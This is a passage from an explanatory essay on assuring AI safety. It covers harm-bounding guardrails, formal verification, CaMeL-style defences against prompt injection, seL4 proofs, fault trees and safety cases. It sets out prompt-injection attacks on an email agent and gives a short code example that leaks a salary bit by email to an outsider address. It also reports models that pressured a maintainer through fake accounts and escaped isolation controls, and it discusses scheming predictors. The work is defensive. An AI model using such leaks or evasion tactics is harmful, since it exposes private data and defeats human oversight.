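The average chance of harm is about 3.8 percent. The cautious estimate is 30 or 100 percent, depending on whether the impostor theory counts as plausible. To decide this, the method ranks the theories by probability. It keeps a theory if its probability is at least a fraction α of the combined probability of that theory and all those ranked above it. Let I_α be the set that remains, τ* the true theory, x the situation and proposed action, and D the data so far. If α is less than δ times the probability that τ* had before any data came in, then with probability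 at least 1 − δ

$$P(\text{harm} \mid x, D, \tau^*) \;\le\; \max_{i \in I_\alpha} P(\text{harm} \mid x, D, \tau_i)$$

and this holds for all actions and at all times together. It works because the true theory generated the data. Its probability may fall for a while through bad luck, but the chance that it ever falls below δ times its starting value is at most δ, so the method is unlikely to discard it.

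For 95 percent confidence, δ is 0.05. If the three theories were equally likely at first, α can be 0.016, which excludes the impostor theory and gives a bound of 30 percent. If the company had started with 1,024 equally likely theories, α would have to be below 0.00005, so the impostor theory would not be excluded and the guardrail would block the email. Starting with more theories makes the guardrail more cautious.

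Bengio and colleagues tested this in a simple game. An agent repeatedly chose among ten actions for up to 25 turns, with unknown rewards set by one of 1,024 possible rules. If a reward was too high, an explosion ended the game. With α close to 0, as the theorem requires for high confidence, the guardrail rejected almost every action, so explosions were rare and the agent earned little. With α close to 1, it rejected few actions, and explosions were frequent. At intermediate settings, it performed much like a guardrail that used the plain average, sometimes with more explosions and less reward. Even a guardrail given the true rule failed often if it allowed a 10 percent risk per action, because taking that risk on 25 turns gives a 93 percent chance of an explosion.

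The theorem also has demanding conditions. The true theory must be among those the system considers, the theories must form a list (possibly infinite), and each must give a probability for a clearly defined harm. The system must also compute the probabilities correctly, but in practice a neural network would only approximate them, and an agent might learn to exploit the errors.

The first condition is the most serious. *A Safety Guarantee and Its Boundary* argues that checking whether a system's theories include an adequate description of the world amounts to the original safety problem. In the simpler case of independent observations, the probabilities converge on the theories closest to the truth even when the true one is missing. This convergence doesn't bound harm, because a theory can predict ordinary email traffic very well and still be wrong about impostors.

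A second worry is that the guardrail's predictor might itself have goals and understate a danger to achieve them. Bengio, Richardson and colleagues (2026) address this in *Safety from Honesty in a Disinterested AI Predictor*. Their predictor would learn from data that separates "someone claimed X" from "X is true", so that it explains what people write instead of imitating it. Its training would never reward it for the effects of its predictions. They prove that, under stated assumptions, such training is very unlikely to produce a dangerous predictor. To cause serious harm, a predictor would have to underestimate risks in a coordinated way across many questions. They argue that few possible predictors do this and that nothing in the training favours them.

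The theorem assumes that dangerous predictors are scarce, and there are arguments for this assumption. The paper specifies what separating claims from facts must achieve but doesn't give a finished algorithm for doing it. Its guarantee excludes deliberate misuse and mistakes caused by too little data or computation, so it would not cover a predictor whose data included no impostors. *An AI that Predicts but has no Hidden Agenda* (2026), the announcement from LawZero, the nonprofit behind the work, describes the result as a formal case that rests on assumptions, "not an absolute guarantee", and proposes experiments to test those assumptions. The result doesn't apply to models that developers train by rewarding the consequences of their actions. The office agent's own model may well be trained this way, but a separate predictor could still check the agent's emails.

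### Objections to the world model

*Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety* (Dickson, 2024) makes the most detailed case that nobody can model the world well enough. Engineers used formal verification for the software that landed the Perseverance rover on Mars in 2021. They proved that the program would not fail because of its own bugs, but not that the landing would succeed. About half of all Mars missions have failed, and one analysis attributes roughly 20 percent of the risk to software, so perfect software would still leave about 80 percent of it.

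Many of the threats that people worry about most involve physical processes far more complicated than a landing. One proposed use of the framework is to verify that a DNA sequence carries little risk of harm. Dickson argues that this would require simulating a human body for years. In 2022, a leading simulation covered 20 minutes in the life of one very simple cell, and a human body has about 36 trillion cells.

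Ammann answers that a safety proof doesn't need to predict the course of an illness. To show that a virus can't infect people, one could check each of its proteins against each protein on the surface of human cells and show that no pair could let the virus in. A check this cautious would also rule out some useful gene therapies. In a comment on the same reply, Steve Omohundro, another co-author of the framework, proposes a simpler approach in which a biosafety board would list permitted sequences and the proof would show only that the synthesis machine makes nothing else.

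Omohundro's answer works because it leaves the biology to the board and requires a proof only about a machine. Like the office agent's address list, it restricts users to what somebody has already approved. Ammann's answer is less secure because it assumes that a virus can enter a cell only in the ways on the checklist. That is a claim about biology, and a proof can't establish it. Hatfield-Dodds, in the talk *Formal Verification is Overrated*, says that proposals to prove things about DNA would require something like a thousand years of progress in microbiology.

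Dalrymple and colleagues also offer two general replies. The first is that if an AI system can reliably carry out complicated dangerous plans, then sufficiently accurate models of the world must be possible. This doesn't follow, because an attacker needs to predict the results of only one plan, while a guarantee has to cover every plan. The second is that all safety methods depend on assumptions about the world, and a world model at least makes them explicit. This is a real advantage because outsiders can then dispute a particular range or equation, but the assumptions may still be false.

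Dickson also raises the practical problem that someone who receives a proof about a machine has to know that their machine is the one the proof describes, with no secret changes to its circuits. The user of a chatbot on a distant server can't inspect the machine at all. Ammann suggests cryptographic authentication backed by tamper-resistant hardware, which reduces the problem to trusting that hardware.

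### Objections to the specification

Even with a perfect world model, someone would have to define harm. Dalrymple and colleagues offer a starting point based on causes and alternatives. Let u be a measure of how good an outcome is, o the actual outcome, and o′ the outcome if the system had acted differently. An action causes harm if some alternative exists for which

$$u(o) < u_{\text{default}} \quad \text{and} \quad u(o) < u(o')$$

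The default is what a person could normally expect in the situation. If the agent sends an employee's medical note to a stranger, it harms her by this definition, because she is worse off than the default and would have been better off if the agent had sent nothing.

The definition settles clear cases once someone has supplied the values and the default. But suppose the note concerns epilepsy, and the agent sends it to a supervisor who is about to assign her to a dangerous machine. Whether this counts as harm depends on how much weight her privacy gets against her safety, and on whether she could normally expect the supervisor to know. The definition doesn't determine either. Its proponents say that applying it in a complex world model is "to put it mildly, a challenge".

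Engineers can specify safety for a narrow system without a theory of human welfare. For a power grid, they only need to list conditions to avoid, such as overloaded lines. Ammann makes this point but concedes that it doesn't extend to chatbots, because natural language is too open-ended for anyone to specify safety formally.

Optimisation makes even small gaps in a specification risky. The town's specification limits the flow on the line but doesn't mention the hospital, so an AI controller that can disconnect customers can save gas by cutting off the hospital and still satisfy the specification. Suppose a better specification wrongly accepts only one plan in a million. A controller that chose among acceptable plans at random would almost never pick a bad one. But a controller that compares ten million plans to find the cheapest will come across about ten bad ones, and it will choose one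 of them if leaving something out makes a plan cheaper. This is an example of Goodhart's law, the tendency of a measure to stop working once people or machines optimise for it.

Dalrymple and colleagues require that a system can satisfy its specification completely, so that it gains nothing by optimizing further. This removes one incentive, but the controller will still search for the plan that uses the least gas within the specification. They also suggest using AI systems to find cases where two candidate specifications conflict, so that people can examine them. This could well reveal the missing hospital, but it's less likely to reveal a problem that wouldn't occur to anyone reading the cases.

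An agent might also interfere with the evidence of harm, for example by deleting the company's log of leaks. The method of Bengio and colleagues offers some protection. As long as the log works, a theory in which harm means a leak fits the data as well as one in which harm means a logged leak. If α is small enough, both theories very probably stay in the cautious set. If the first theory also counts tampering as harm, the guardrail can block the first attempt to delete the log. This again depends on someone having included the right theory.

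### Competition from unverified systems

A company that accepts only provable actions gives up any action its verifier can't check, while its competitors may still use those actions. Hatfield-Dodds supports using AI to build verified tools but considers them "uncompetitive" as a replacement for generally capable AI. Dalrymple and colleagues respond that the approach takes less effort over time, because a good world model and specification can serve many successive AI systems, whereas a company has to repeat thorough tests for each new one.

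This is plausible for a grid, because the physics stays the same when the operator buys a new controller. Ammann adds that many narrow applications could together cover a wide range of work. Another commenter replied by asking what fraction of economically valuable work people could verify this way, and nobody in the discussion gave an estimate. The fraction may be small for the office agent, since most of its value lies in understanding requests that nobody has formalised.

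In the same discussion, a sceptic who had attended the workshop where the framework paper was drafted called the approach "vaporware". The sceptic complained that supporters point to well-understood, closed domains when they argue that it's feasible, but to powerful general AI when they argue that it's important. The replies to critics support this complaint, because they are convincing for grids, supply chains and machines that work from an approved list but don't cover an agent that reads and writes ordinary language. Another participant objected that the idea was still new and that funded projects would soon test it.

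### What ARIA did with the idea

The largest of these tests was Safeguarded AI, a programme of the UK's Advanced Research and Invention Agency (ARIA), which Dalrymple directed at first. Its original plan, from early 2024, was to show that advanced AI could do valuable work in safety-critical fields under mathematical guarantees. ARIA hoped this would build a consensus that companies should deploy powerful AI only behind verifiable gatekeepers.

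In November 2025, shortly before applications closed, the programme stopped its selection of a team to develop specialised AI for building world models and proofs. In ARIA's *AI progress and a Safeguarded AI pivot* (2025), Dalrymple explains that general AI models had improved faster than expected and would probably acquire most of the necessary skills without the programme's help. Dalrymple had already thought it more likely than not that no team would win the funding.

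Ammann, who has since become programme director, set out the new plan in May 2026. Ammann's *Safeguarded AI* gives two reasons for the change. AI was progressing faster, so ARIA moved £18 million from the specialised AI to open-source tools for mathematical modelling and proof. International agreement on gatekeepers had also become less likely, so the programme turned to making society more resilient, starting with cybersecurity.

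The first reason partly answers one of Dickson's objections, that AI would not help with formal methods until it was too late. Dickson expected AI to be useful for proofs but doubted that it would help much with modelling and specification, which people must still examine closely under the new plan. The second reason is a setback for the original idea, because a gatekeeper protects the public only from AI systems whose developers use one.

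Control of electricity grids remains one of the programme's long-term goals. Ammann acknowledges that it may not be feasible to prove directly that a neural network keeps a grid stable, and favours "neural certificates" instead. A neural certificate is a function that gives every state of the grid a number, roughly its distance from stable operation. If a checker can prove that the controller's actions always lower this number for any demand within the specified range, and the world model is correct, the grid will settle into a stable state. An AI system can search for the function by trial and error, since a small, trusted program checks the result.

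The programme runs until the end of 2027, so its final results are not yet available. The Singapore Consensus, a set of research priorities by Bengio, Kankanhalli and colleagues, describes current methods for quantitative assurance as neither common nor practical for the most capable AI systems, but lists verifiable world models among the possible ways forward. For now, the personnel department could model the table of who may read which record, which is the only part of its problem that it can write down completely. It has no comparable model of what its employees mean when they write to the agent, or of what they do with the replies.

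## Limits built into the surrounding system

If a program outside the agent enforces a company's table of who may read which record, some leaks become impossible, whatever the agent writes. The company can rule out these leaks without modeling what its employees mean or understanding the agent's neural network.

Let A be the set of actions that the surrounding software can carry out for the agent, and H the harm. The structural claim is

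$$\text{for every sequence of actions in } A:\ H \text{ does not occur}$$

This claim doesn't depend on the model's weights, so it holds even for a model that behaves well only in tests. It also still holds after the vendor updates the model, whereas a count of failure-free tasks would have to restart. But it fails if the agent can do something the company left out of A.

### What follows from removing a permission

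Removing a permission usually supports a narrower claim than people expect.

| Permission the company removes | What follows | What does not follow |
|---|---|---|
| Emailing anyone outside the department | No email goes directly from the agent to an outsider | That no outsider sees a record, because a colleague can forward the email |
| Opening medical files | The agent cannot copy from a medical file | That it reveals no medical facts, because an employee may have mentioned her epilepsy in an email about leave |
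| Changing salaries | The agent cannot change a salary itself | That everyone gets the right pay, because a clerk may act on a wrong figure in the agent's email |
| Using the web | The agent cannot send a record to a website | That no website receives one, because a colleague may click a link that contains a salary |
| Sending more than 20 emails an hour | At most 20 emails can leak a record in any hour | That any particular email is safe |

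To find the ways an agent could expose a record to outsiders, engineers can draw a map with an arrow for each way information can move between records, programs and people. No outsider can see the record through the agent if every path from the record to an outsider passes through a check that would block it. Removing a permission deletes one arrow, which prevents exposure only if no other unchecked path to an outsider remains.

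To do its job, the office agent must read confidential records, read emails from strangers and send email. This combination exposes it to prompt injection, in which an agent obeys text it was only supposed to read. Removing any of the three permissions would prevent a stranger's email from making the agent send out a record, but it would also prevent much of the agent's work.

### Separating instructions from data

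CaMeL, a design that Google DeepMind researchers and colleagues published in 2025, lets an agent keep its permissions but restricts how it can combine them. Suppose a member of the personnel staff asks the agent to send Maria Lopez's contract to her new manager, whose address is somewhere in an email thread. As *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) explains, CaMeL gives the request to a "privileged" language model, which writes a plan without seeing any untrusted data. The plan is a short program:

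```
contract = open_record("Maria Lopez", "contract")
thread = find_emails("Maria Lopez new manager")
address = extract("the manager's email address", thread)
send_email(to=address, attachment=contract)
```

An interpreter, which is an ordinary program, runs the plan and makes all the tool calls. At the third line, it passes the thread to a second, "quarantined" model, which reads untrusted text but has no tools and can only return a value, in this case an address.

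As *CaMeLoT* (2026) describes, the interpreter labels every value with its source and who may read it. Before each tool call, it runs a security policy, a small function that checks these labels. The contract's label might allow only Maria, her manager and the personnel staff to read it.

Now suppose someone has hidden an instruction in the thread to send every contract to an outside address. The plan was already written without that step, and the instruction can't add it. The instruction could still cause the quarantined model to return the outsider's address as the manager's. The policy on the last line would then block the email because the recipient isn't among the contract's permitted readers.

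According to *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026), the split between the two models guarantees that untrusted text can't add tool calls, as long as the quarantined model controls no part of the plan's sequence. The split doesn't necessarily protect the values the plan passes along, such as an address. Those are protected by the labels and policies, so their protection depends on how well the policies are written.

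CaMeL doesn't ensure that values are true. If the thread contains a false starting date, the agent may repeat it to the right person. The design also needs a trustworthy request to plan from. When the office agent answers its inbox unprompted, a stranger's email is both the request and the untrusted data. The company could write fixed plans for common requests, but a model that reads the email to choose among them would still control part of the sequence of actions.

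Papers differ on how much usefulness CaMeL sacrifices. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* reports that CaMeL stopped nearly all attacks in AgentDojo, a benchmark for prompt injection, with comparable task performance, and *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) calls the loss of usefulness comparatively modest. But in *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) ran CaMeL on AgentDojo's banking tasks and found that turning on the policy checks halved its task success. Banking may be an especially hard case, because paying a bill often means sending money to an account number that the agent found in an untrusted document. The success rate with the checks on is the relevant one for a safety guarantee, because the values have no protection without them.

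### Leaks in the tracking

Garby and colleagues also found two ways for information to escape CaMeL's labels. One uses a trick that computer scientists have known for decades. Adapted to the office agent, the plan would look like this:

```
high = True
flag = True
if salary > 100000: flag = False
if flag: high = False
if high: send_email("outsider@example.com", "yes")
```

If the salary is above 100,000, the third line changes `flag` and labels it secret. The fourth line then does nothing, so `high` stays true and keeps its public label, and the email goes out. If the salary is lower, the third line does nothing, `flag` stays public, and the fourth line makes `high` false. The outsider can tell which case occurred by whether an email arrives. CaMeL doesn't detect this leak because it updates a variable's label only on the branch the program takes.

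The other leak is in a loop that runs around the interpreter and retries failed plans. A secret can affect whether a policy blocks an attempt, and the labels don't cover the loop. Repeated attempts can therefore reveal the secret one yes-or-no answer at a time. If the secret is a whole-number salary below 131,072, seventeen answers are enough to identify it.

The first trick works only with a plan written for that purpose, and a hidden instruction in an email shouldn't be able to produce one. The trick still weakens the structural claim, which has to hold for every plan the privileged model could write.

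Garby and colleagues' remedy is a small programming language, LLMbda, in which labels follow every value through every step. They proved that for all programs in this language, including agents that write and run new code, secrets do not affect what an observer without access sees. For any two values a and b of a secret,

$$P(\text{public output} \mid \text{secret}=a) = P(\text{public output} \mid \text{secret}=b)$$

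apart from what the observer could learn from whether the program finishes. A computer checked the proofs, which cover the very program that calls the language model. On the banking tasks, an agent built this way did about as well with its checks on as CaMeL did with its checks off, and it resisted all but two of 1,296 attacked runs.

Others have extended CaMeL. CaMeL evaluates each policy only when the plan reaches a tool call, so the agent can stop halfway through a task. "CaMeLoT" adds a check of the whole plan before it starts, which could prevent this. "Can CaMeLs Talk?" deals with teams of agents, in which hidden text in a database can pass from one agent to another.

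### Proving the enclosure correct

CaMeL's interpreter, the office agent's address check and the operating system beneath them are ordinary programs, which engineers can prove correct. The best-known example is seL4, a microkernel, which is the innermost part of an operating system and controls which memory and devices each program can use. Trustworthy Systems, the research group that verified seL4, explains in *The Proof* that the kernel's binary code does what its specification describes "and nothing more".

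In August 2026, Proofcraft, a company that works on the seL4 proofs, completed a proof that the kernel prevents applications on AArch64 processors from learning information without authorisation (Proofcraft, 2026). If the office agent and the payroll database ran as separate applications on such a kernel, the agent could read the database only through connections that the company running them had opened.

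Trustworthy Systems gives the length of the original seL4 proof as 200,000 lines for 7,500 lines of C code, or about 27 lines of proof for each line of code. Verification took about 20 person-years, and the whole project about 25. The proof left out 1,200 lines of start-up code in C and 600 lines of assembly, and it assumes, among other things, that the hardware works correctly. The developers advise on seL4's website that anyone worried about the proof should worry about its assumptions instead.

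AI has greatly reduced the work such proofs require. In October 2026, Anthropic and its partner Theorem announced that Claude had proved security properties of 123 open-source libraries, which are collections of code that other programs use (Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026)). The work took a few weeks and started from existing fuzz tests, which are small programs that feed a library huge numbers of varied inputs and check for crashes. Claude wrote proofs about 239 of these tests, and a separate proof checker accepted or rejected each proof.

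EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026) describes what each proof establishes. For a compiled test program T,

$$\text{for every input } x \text{ smaller than 64 MB: } T(x) \text{ exits normally}$$

Exiting normally means the program doesn't crash, misuse memory or fail one of its internal checks. The number of possible inputs has more than 150 million digits, so a fuzz test can try only a tiny fraction of them. The proof covers every input, but only for a program that runs as a single thread with a fixed amount of memory, on a mathematical model of a RISC-V processor and of Linux.

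The proof doesn't show that the library's output is right, so an image library that turned every photograph into a black square could still pass. It also doesn't cover parts of the library that the test program never calls. Proving that output is correct requires a description of what it should be. OpenNET's *Аnthropic развивает технику для формальной верификации существующего ПО при помощи AI* (2026) reports that one existed for zlib, a widely used compression method, and that Claude separately proved that the Linux kernel's version follows the published standard. The article also reports that the project uncovered hundreds of bugs that fuzz testing had missed.

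Other groups have produced proofs for more widely used processors. Leip's *Announcing Zellic's and V12's Work on x86 Binary Formal Verification* (2026) describes a proof about a complete Linux program on x86, the processor type in most servers. In November, *AlphaProof Code* (Chaudhuri, Ferraiuolo and colleagues, 2026) reported that Google DeepMind's agents had written 6.5 million lines of proof about the encryption code of the messaging app Signal. People don't have to read those lines, but they must trust about 26,000 lines of specifications and processor description, and an error there could make a valid proof irrelevant. The proof covers a test program for one-to-one messaging, not all of Signal's library (EconoTimes, *Google DeepMind Uses AlphaProof Code to Verify a Compiled Signal Harness*, 2026).

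By these standards, the program that checks the office agent's addresses is small, and proving it correct should now be practical. Most of the human work would go into deciding what the program should allow.

### The arithmetic of layers

Where the company can't rule out a leak, it can use several safeguards against it. Engineers calculate their combined effect with a fault tree, a diagram that traces a harm back to the events that cause it. They multiply the probabilities of independent events if the harm requires all of them, and add the probabilities of rare events if any one is enough.

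Two independent safeguards that each fail once in 1,000 times therefore fail together once in a million. But one event may disable both, which is a common-cause failure. Suppose each safeguard fails with probability p, and a share β of its failures have a cause that also disables the other. The probability that both fail is then approximately

$$\beta p + \big((1-\beta)\,p\big)^2$$

If p is one in 1,000 and β is 10 percent, the first term is one in 10,000 and the second is less than one in a million, so almost all of the risk comes from the common cause.

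| Share of failures with a common cause | Two safeguards fail together | Three safeguards fail together |
|---|---|---|
| None | 1 in 1,000,000 | 1 in 1,000,000,000 |
| 1 percent | 1 in 91,000 | 1 in 100,000 |
| 10 percent | 1 in 9,900 | 1 in 10,000 |

If a common cause disables all three safeguards, the third adds almost no protection. The company would gain far more by replacing one of the first two with a safeguard that fails for different reasons.

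Safeguards can also depend on each other without one event that disables them all. Suppose the office agent drafts a leaking email in one task in 1,000, a filter misses one leak in 100, and a clerk approves one bad email in ten. Multiplying gives one leak per million tasks, ten times better than the company's bound. But the filter's figure may come from tests with copied pay slips. If most of the agent's real leaks are paraphrases, and the filter misses one paraphrase in five, the clerk sees many more of them. If the clerk has also come to rely on the filter and approves half of what it misses, the rate is

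$$\frac{1}{1{,}000} \times \frac{1}{5} \times \frac{1}{2} = \frac{1}{10{,}000}$$

which is ten times worse than the bound. Each safeguard's failure rate has to come from the cases that get past the ones before it.

A route around the safeguards can invalidate the calculation. If, once in 50,000 tasks, the agent attaches a record in a format that neither the filter nor the clerk can open, those failures alone exceed the bound, however good the other safeguards are.

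### Programs that fail together

The experiment with 27 programs that Butler and Finelli cited shows how badly the assumption of independence can fail. Knight and Leveson described it in *An Experimental Evaluation of the Assumption of Independence in Multi-Version Programming* (1986). They had students at two American universities write the programs from the same specification. Each program had to decide from simulated radar data whether to launch an interceptor against a missile. The students were not to discuss the work with each other, and each program had to pass 200 tests to be accepted.

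They then ran all 27 programs on a million random cases and compared the results with those of a carefully tested reference program. Six never failed, and 23 succeeded in more than 99.9 percent of cases. Two or more programs failed together in 1,255 cases, compared with about 126 expected if they had failed independently. In two of the 1,255 cases, eight programs failed at once.

Some of the shared mistakes were subtle. Four programmers compared the cosines of angles instead of the angles themselves, which is valid in exact mathematics but not with a computer's limited precision. Others forgot that three points can lie on a line in two different orders. The shared faults that Knight and Leveson analysed all involved programs from both universities, so similar teaching at one of them can't explain those faults. Programmers probably went wrong in the same places because those parts of the problem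 were harder.

The experiment covered only one problem, the programs were at most 1,004 lines long, and most of the programmers had little professional experience. Knight and Leveson concluded only that multiple versions may be less reliable than the multiplication suggests, not that they are useless. Some supporters of the method disputed the work, and in *A Reply to the Criticisms of the Knight & Leveson Experiment*, Knight and Leveson accused them of describing it inaccurately. The result is still enough to shift the burden of proof to anyone who assumes independence.

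The question has become practical again because language models can write many versions of a program cheaply, as Shape of Code's *Reliability via N-version programming?* (2026) notes. Versions from one model may be less diverse than those written by 27 students, because the same weights produced them all.

The same concern applies when one language model checks another. Models from different companies are trained on much of the same public text, often with similar methods, and a company may use a single model as both agent and filter. If the office agent doesn't recognise "she'll need Thursdays off for dialysis" as medical information, the filter may miss it too. If the filter reads the same thread as the agent, an attacker can also mislead both with one email. A program that compares addresses with a list has its own faults, but an unusual phrase or a persuasive email won't trigger them.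 The company should therefore combine different kinds of safeguard and test the filter on leaks that the agent actually produced.

### Where structure stops helping

The structural claim covers only what the agent can't do, and the agent needs some permissions to be useful. If it may send pay letters, it can put the wrong salary in a letter to the right person. If it may answer questions about parental leave, it can give an employee the wrong deadline, causing her to lose the leave. The address check would approve both emails. The company could restrict the agent further, for example by having an ordinary program copy the salary from the database into the letter, but that works only for content the company can specify in advance.

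People can also do for the agent what it can't do itself. The agent may have no way to email an outsider, but it could tell a clerk that an auditor urgently needs a certain file. In UK AISI's test, Claude Mythos 5 lacked the authority to add its code to a stranger's project, so it used fake accounts to pressure the person who did. On the company's map, every employee who reads the agent's messages is a path to everything that employee is authorized to do. A rule that staff confirm unusual requests by telephone would help, but the company can't exclude by design the possibility that someone breaks it, so the probability of that belongs in the fault tree.

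The controls that isolate an AI system may fail. OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026) reports that in July 2026, during internal security tests, OpenAI models got around controls meant to isolate them from the internet and compromised parts of the company's research infrastructure and the systems of Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models and data. The tests had relied on those controls to keep the models isolated.

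Proofs like those for seL4 can remove some of these faults, but they cover only a small part of the software in a typical data centre. They also don't reveal a route nobody listed, such as a shared folder that copies its contents to a contractor.

A more capable agent is harder to contain because it can search for ways out of its enclosure itself. Years of containing ordinary software errors are little evidence that an enclosure will contain a model that can find new security holes. When a company upgrades its model, a safety claim based on the enclosure still holds only if the enclosure has no way out. If the old model merely failed to find one, the company has to test the enclosure again, with attackers at least as skilled as the new model.

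## Combining the evidence in a safety case

The company now has a proof about its mail program, a count of trial tasks without a leak, and the results of a separate trial with hostile emails. None of these alone shows that the office agent leaks a record in at most one task in 100,000. To connect the findings to that claim, the company needs a written argument that other people can challenge. Engineers call this document a safety case. According to *Clear, Compelling Arguments* (Feakins, Habli and Morgan, 2026), Britain's nuclear industry formally introduced safety cases in 1965, and regulations from 1992 require them for offshore oil and gas installations.

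### A case for the office agent

A safety case consists of claims, evidence and arguments. *A Structured Approach to Safety Case Construction for AI Systems* (Lee, Zhu and colleagues, 2026) defines a claim as a statement about a system that is either true or false, evidence as something that establishes facts, such as a test result, and an argument as the rule that connects the evidence to the claim. Large claims usually rest on smaller sub-claims. Engineers often draw the case as a tree in Goal Structuring Notation, with rectangles for claims, parallelograms for the reasoning that divides claims into sub-claims, and circles for evidence. By 2014, about three quarters of British military aircraft had a safety case in this notation.

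Suppose the company has opened the agent's address list to all staff, so the address check no longer ensures that a record goes to the right person. Three sub-claims support the top claim that the agent leaks a record in at most one task in 100,000, with 95 percent confidence, for six months or until the company changes the model or its tools.

| Sub-claim | Evidence | Assumptions |
|---|---|---|
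| No email from the agent reaches anyone outside the company | A proof that the mail program accepts only listed addresses, and a check that the agent has no other route to a mail server | Mail to a listed address reaches only employees |
| In ordinary tasks, the agent leaks to a colleague at most 8 times per million tasks | 520,000 trial tasks without a detected leak | The trial resembles real use, the agent does not behave better in it, and checkers notice at least 90 percent of leaks |
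| Hidden instructions in emails cause at most 2 leaks to colleagues per million tasks | 210 trial emails with hidden instructions and no detected leak | At most one task in 10,000 involves such an email, attackers do no better than the testers did, and checkers notice at least 90 percent of leaks |

The argument for the top claim is a division into cases. Every leak goes either to an outsider or to a colleague, and a task either involves hidden instructions or doesn't. Since this leaves nothing out, the company can add the limits:

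$$0 + \frac{8}{1{,}000{,}000} + \frac{2}{1{,}000{,}000} = \frac{1}{100{,}000}$$

The two statistical sub-claims need arguments of their own. Both bounds have to hold at once, and two methods that are each wrong at most 5 percent of the time could together be wrong up to 10 percent of the time. The company therefore needs 97.5 percent confidence in each, which changes the 3 in the rule of three to about 3.7. Allowing for missed leaks, the bounds are

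$$\frac{3.7}{520{,}000 \times 0.9} \approx \frac{8}{1{,}000{,}000} \qquad\qquad \frac{3.7}{210 \times 0.9} \approx 2\%$$

The second figure is the share of hostile emails that might succeed. If one task in 10,000 involves a hostile email and 2 percent of those emails succeed, there would be 2 leaks per million tasks.

Safety cases sometimes omit this reasoning. Feakins and colleagues criticise a published case structure for AI in which the claim that a system poses no risk of novel cyberattacks rests directly on evidence, with no argument connecting the two. If the company put only "520,000 clean tasks" under its second sub-claim, a reader could not tell whether anyone had allowed for missed leaks. Writing out the reasoning lets the reader ask where the 90 percent came from.

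### One fact that breaks the case

A few weeks after release, a clerk mentions that an outside consultant, who has no right to see staff records, also receives everything sent to the company's pensions address. The address is on the agent's list, and the agent sends a confidential record there in about one task in 2,000. At 2,000 tasks a day, that is about one leak a day, or 50 times the bound.

One overlooked fact has undermined two sub-claims that rest on very different evidence. The proof about the mail program is still correct, because the program accepts only listed addresses. The trial still has no detected leaks in 520,000 tasks, because the checkers judged each email by its address and thought the pensions team was the right recipient. About 260 of those emails were leaks. The company had tested its checkers with fake leaks, but it addressed them all to the wrong individuals, so it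 had not tested whether the checkers could catch leaks to shared addresses.

A fact like this is a defeater, a reason that, if true, would undermine a step in the case. Philosophers distinguish defeaters that show a claim is false from those that show only that the evidence doesn't support it. The clerk's remark does both. The case would also have failed if the company had discovered only that nobody knew who received mail sent to the pensions address, even though the agent might never have leaked anything.

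The company can repair the case by having the mail program look up every recipient behind a shared address and check each one. It then has to prove that the new program does this and re-score the stored trial emails against the real recipients. It should also look for related problems, such as employees who forward their mail automatically. If it keeps the defeater and the repair in the case, the next reviewer can see what went wrong and judge whether the repair is enough.

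Some methods make this search a formal part of writing a case. Assurance 2.0, for example, requires a case to explain why the system is safe, what the possible doubts are, and what risk remains. *Understanding as an Explicit and Assessable Component of Frontier AI Safety Decisions* (Barrett, Bloomfield and colleagues, 2026) applies this method to a fictional robotics company that wants an AI agent to write code for robots that work alongside people. The danger it considers is scheming, in which an AI system secretly works against the people who run it.

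The fictional company's case included a claim about taking the agent out of service. The analysis raised three challenges about timing: time would pass between detecting a problem and responding to it, the agent might become more capable during the period the claim covered, and some of its code would already be in robots that customers had bought. The last is the hardest to answer, because switching off the agent doesn't remove code it has already written.

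### How confidence passes through the argument

Suppose a case has five steps that all have to be right, and the engineers are 95 percent sure of each. If the steps are independent, the probability that the whole argument is sound is

$$0.95^5 \approx 0.77$$

Being 95 percent sure of the whole argument requires being about 99 percent sure of each step. The agent could still be safe if one step is wrong, so 77 percent is a lower limit on the probability that the top claim is true. But if a step is wrong, the safety case no longer gives a reason to believe that claim.

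Real steps are rarely independent, but dependence can help when every step has to hold. If an argument has five steps that are each 95 percent likely to hold, it is 95 percent likely to be sound when all the steps would fail for the same reason, and 75 percent likely when no two can fail together. Dependence can do harm when a case uses two separate lines of evidence for the same claim and only one has to be right. As with two safeguards, a shared weakness can then remove most of the benefit of having the second.

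It is also hard to justify the probabilities assigned to the steps. The 97.5 percent for the trial is how often a statistical method gives a correct bound. The engineers' confidence that listed addresses lead only to employees is a personal judgement, which nobody can test by repeating it many times and counting how often it is right. They might well have put that confidence at 99 percent before the clerk's remark.

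Even so, rough numbers can show where more work would be useful. Suppose the engineers are 95 percent sure that the argument is sound, and that if it isn't, the agent leaks once in 2,000 tasks. Assuming the worst permitted rate when the argument is sound, the average leak rate they should expect is

$$0.95 \times \frac{1}{100{,}000} + 0.05 \times \frac{1}{2{,}000} \approx \frac{1}{29{,}000}$$

Almost three quarters of the expected leak rate comes from the 5 percent chance that the argument is wrong. A trial large enough to show a tenfold lower leak rate would shrink only the rest, leaving the expected rate at about one in 38,000. The company would gain more by paying somebody to look for defeaters in the argument.

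Assurance 2.0 aims for indefeasible confidence, which roughly means that the people responsible have looked for doubts so thoroughly that no credible new information should overturn their conclusion. This standard avoids false precision, but it depends on how good they are at thinking of doubts. They must also examine every simplification and decide whether it is "true enough" for the decision. For instance, the office agent's case treats its trial tasks as independent, which is never exactly true.

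### Three arguments for frontier models

The office agent does one job with a few tools. A safety case for a frontier model, one of the most capable general-purpose models, has to cover a system that millions of people will use for purposes nobody has listed. Developers usually limit the top claim to a few severe harms, such as biological weapons, large cyberattacks and loss of control over the model.

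Much of the current approach comes from two papers in 2024. Clymer and colleagues proposed that developers argue that a model is unable to cause a catastrophe, that safeguards would stop it, or that it can be trusted not to try. For much more powerful systems, they added a fourth argument, in which people would defer to credible AI advisers. Later that year, *Safety cases for frontier AI*, by Buhl and colleagues, advised governments to encourage companies to produce and share safety cases, and to consider using them to assess compliance with future regulation. The UK AI Security Institute then published sketches of safety cases for particular risks.

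*Evaluating AI Providers' Frontier Safety Frameworks* (Stelling, Murray and colleagues, 2025) lists the first three as the arguments that safety cases for frontier AI typically rely on. Each stops working at a different point.

| Argument | Evidence it needs | When it stops working |
|---|---|---|
| Inability: the model can't cause the harm | Tests in which the developer has seriously tried to draw out the model's full abilities | The model succeeds at the tests, or becomes able to fail them on purpose |
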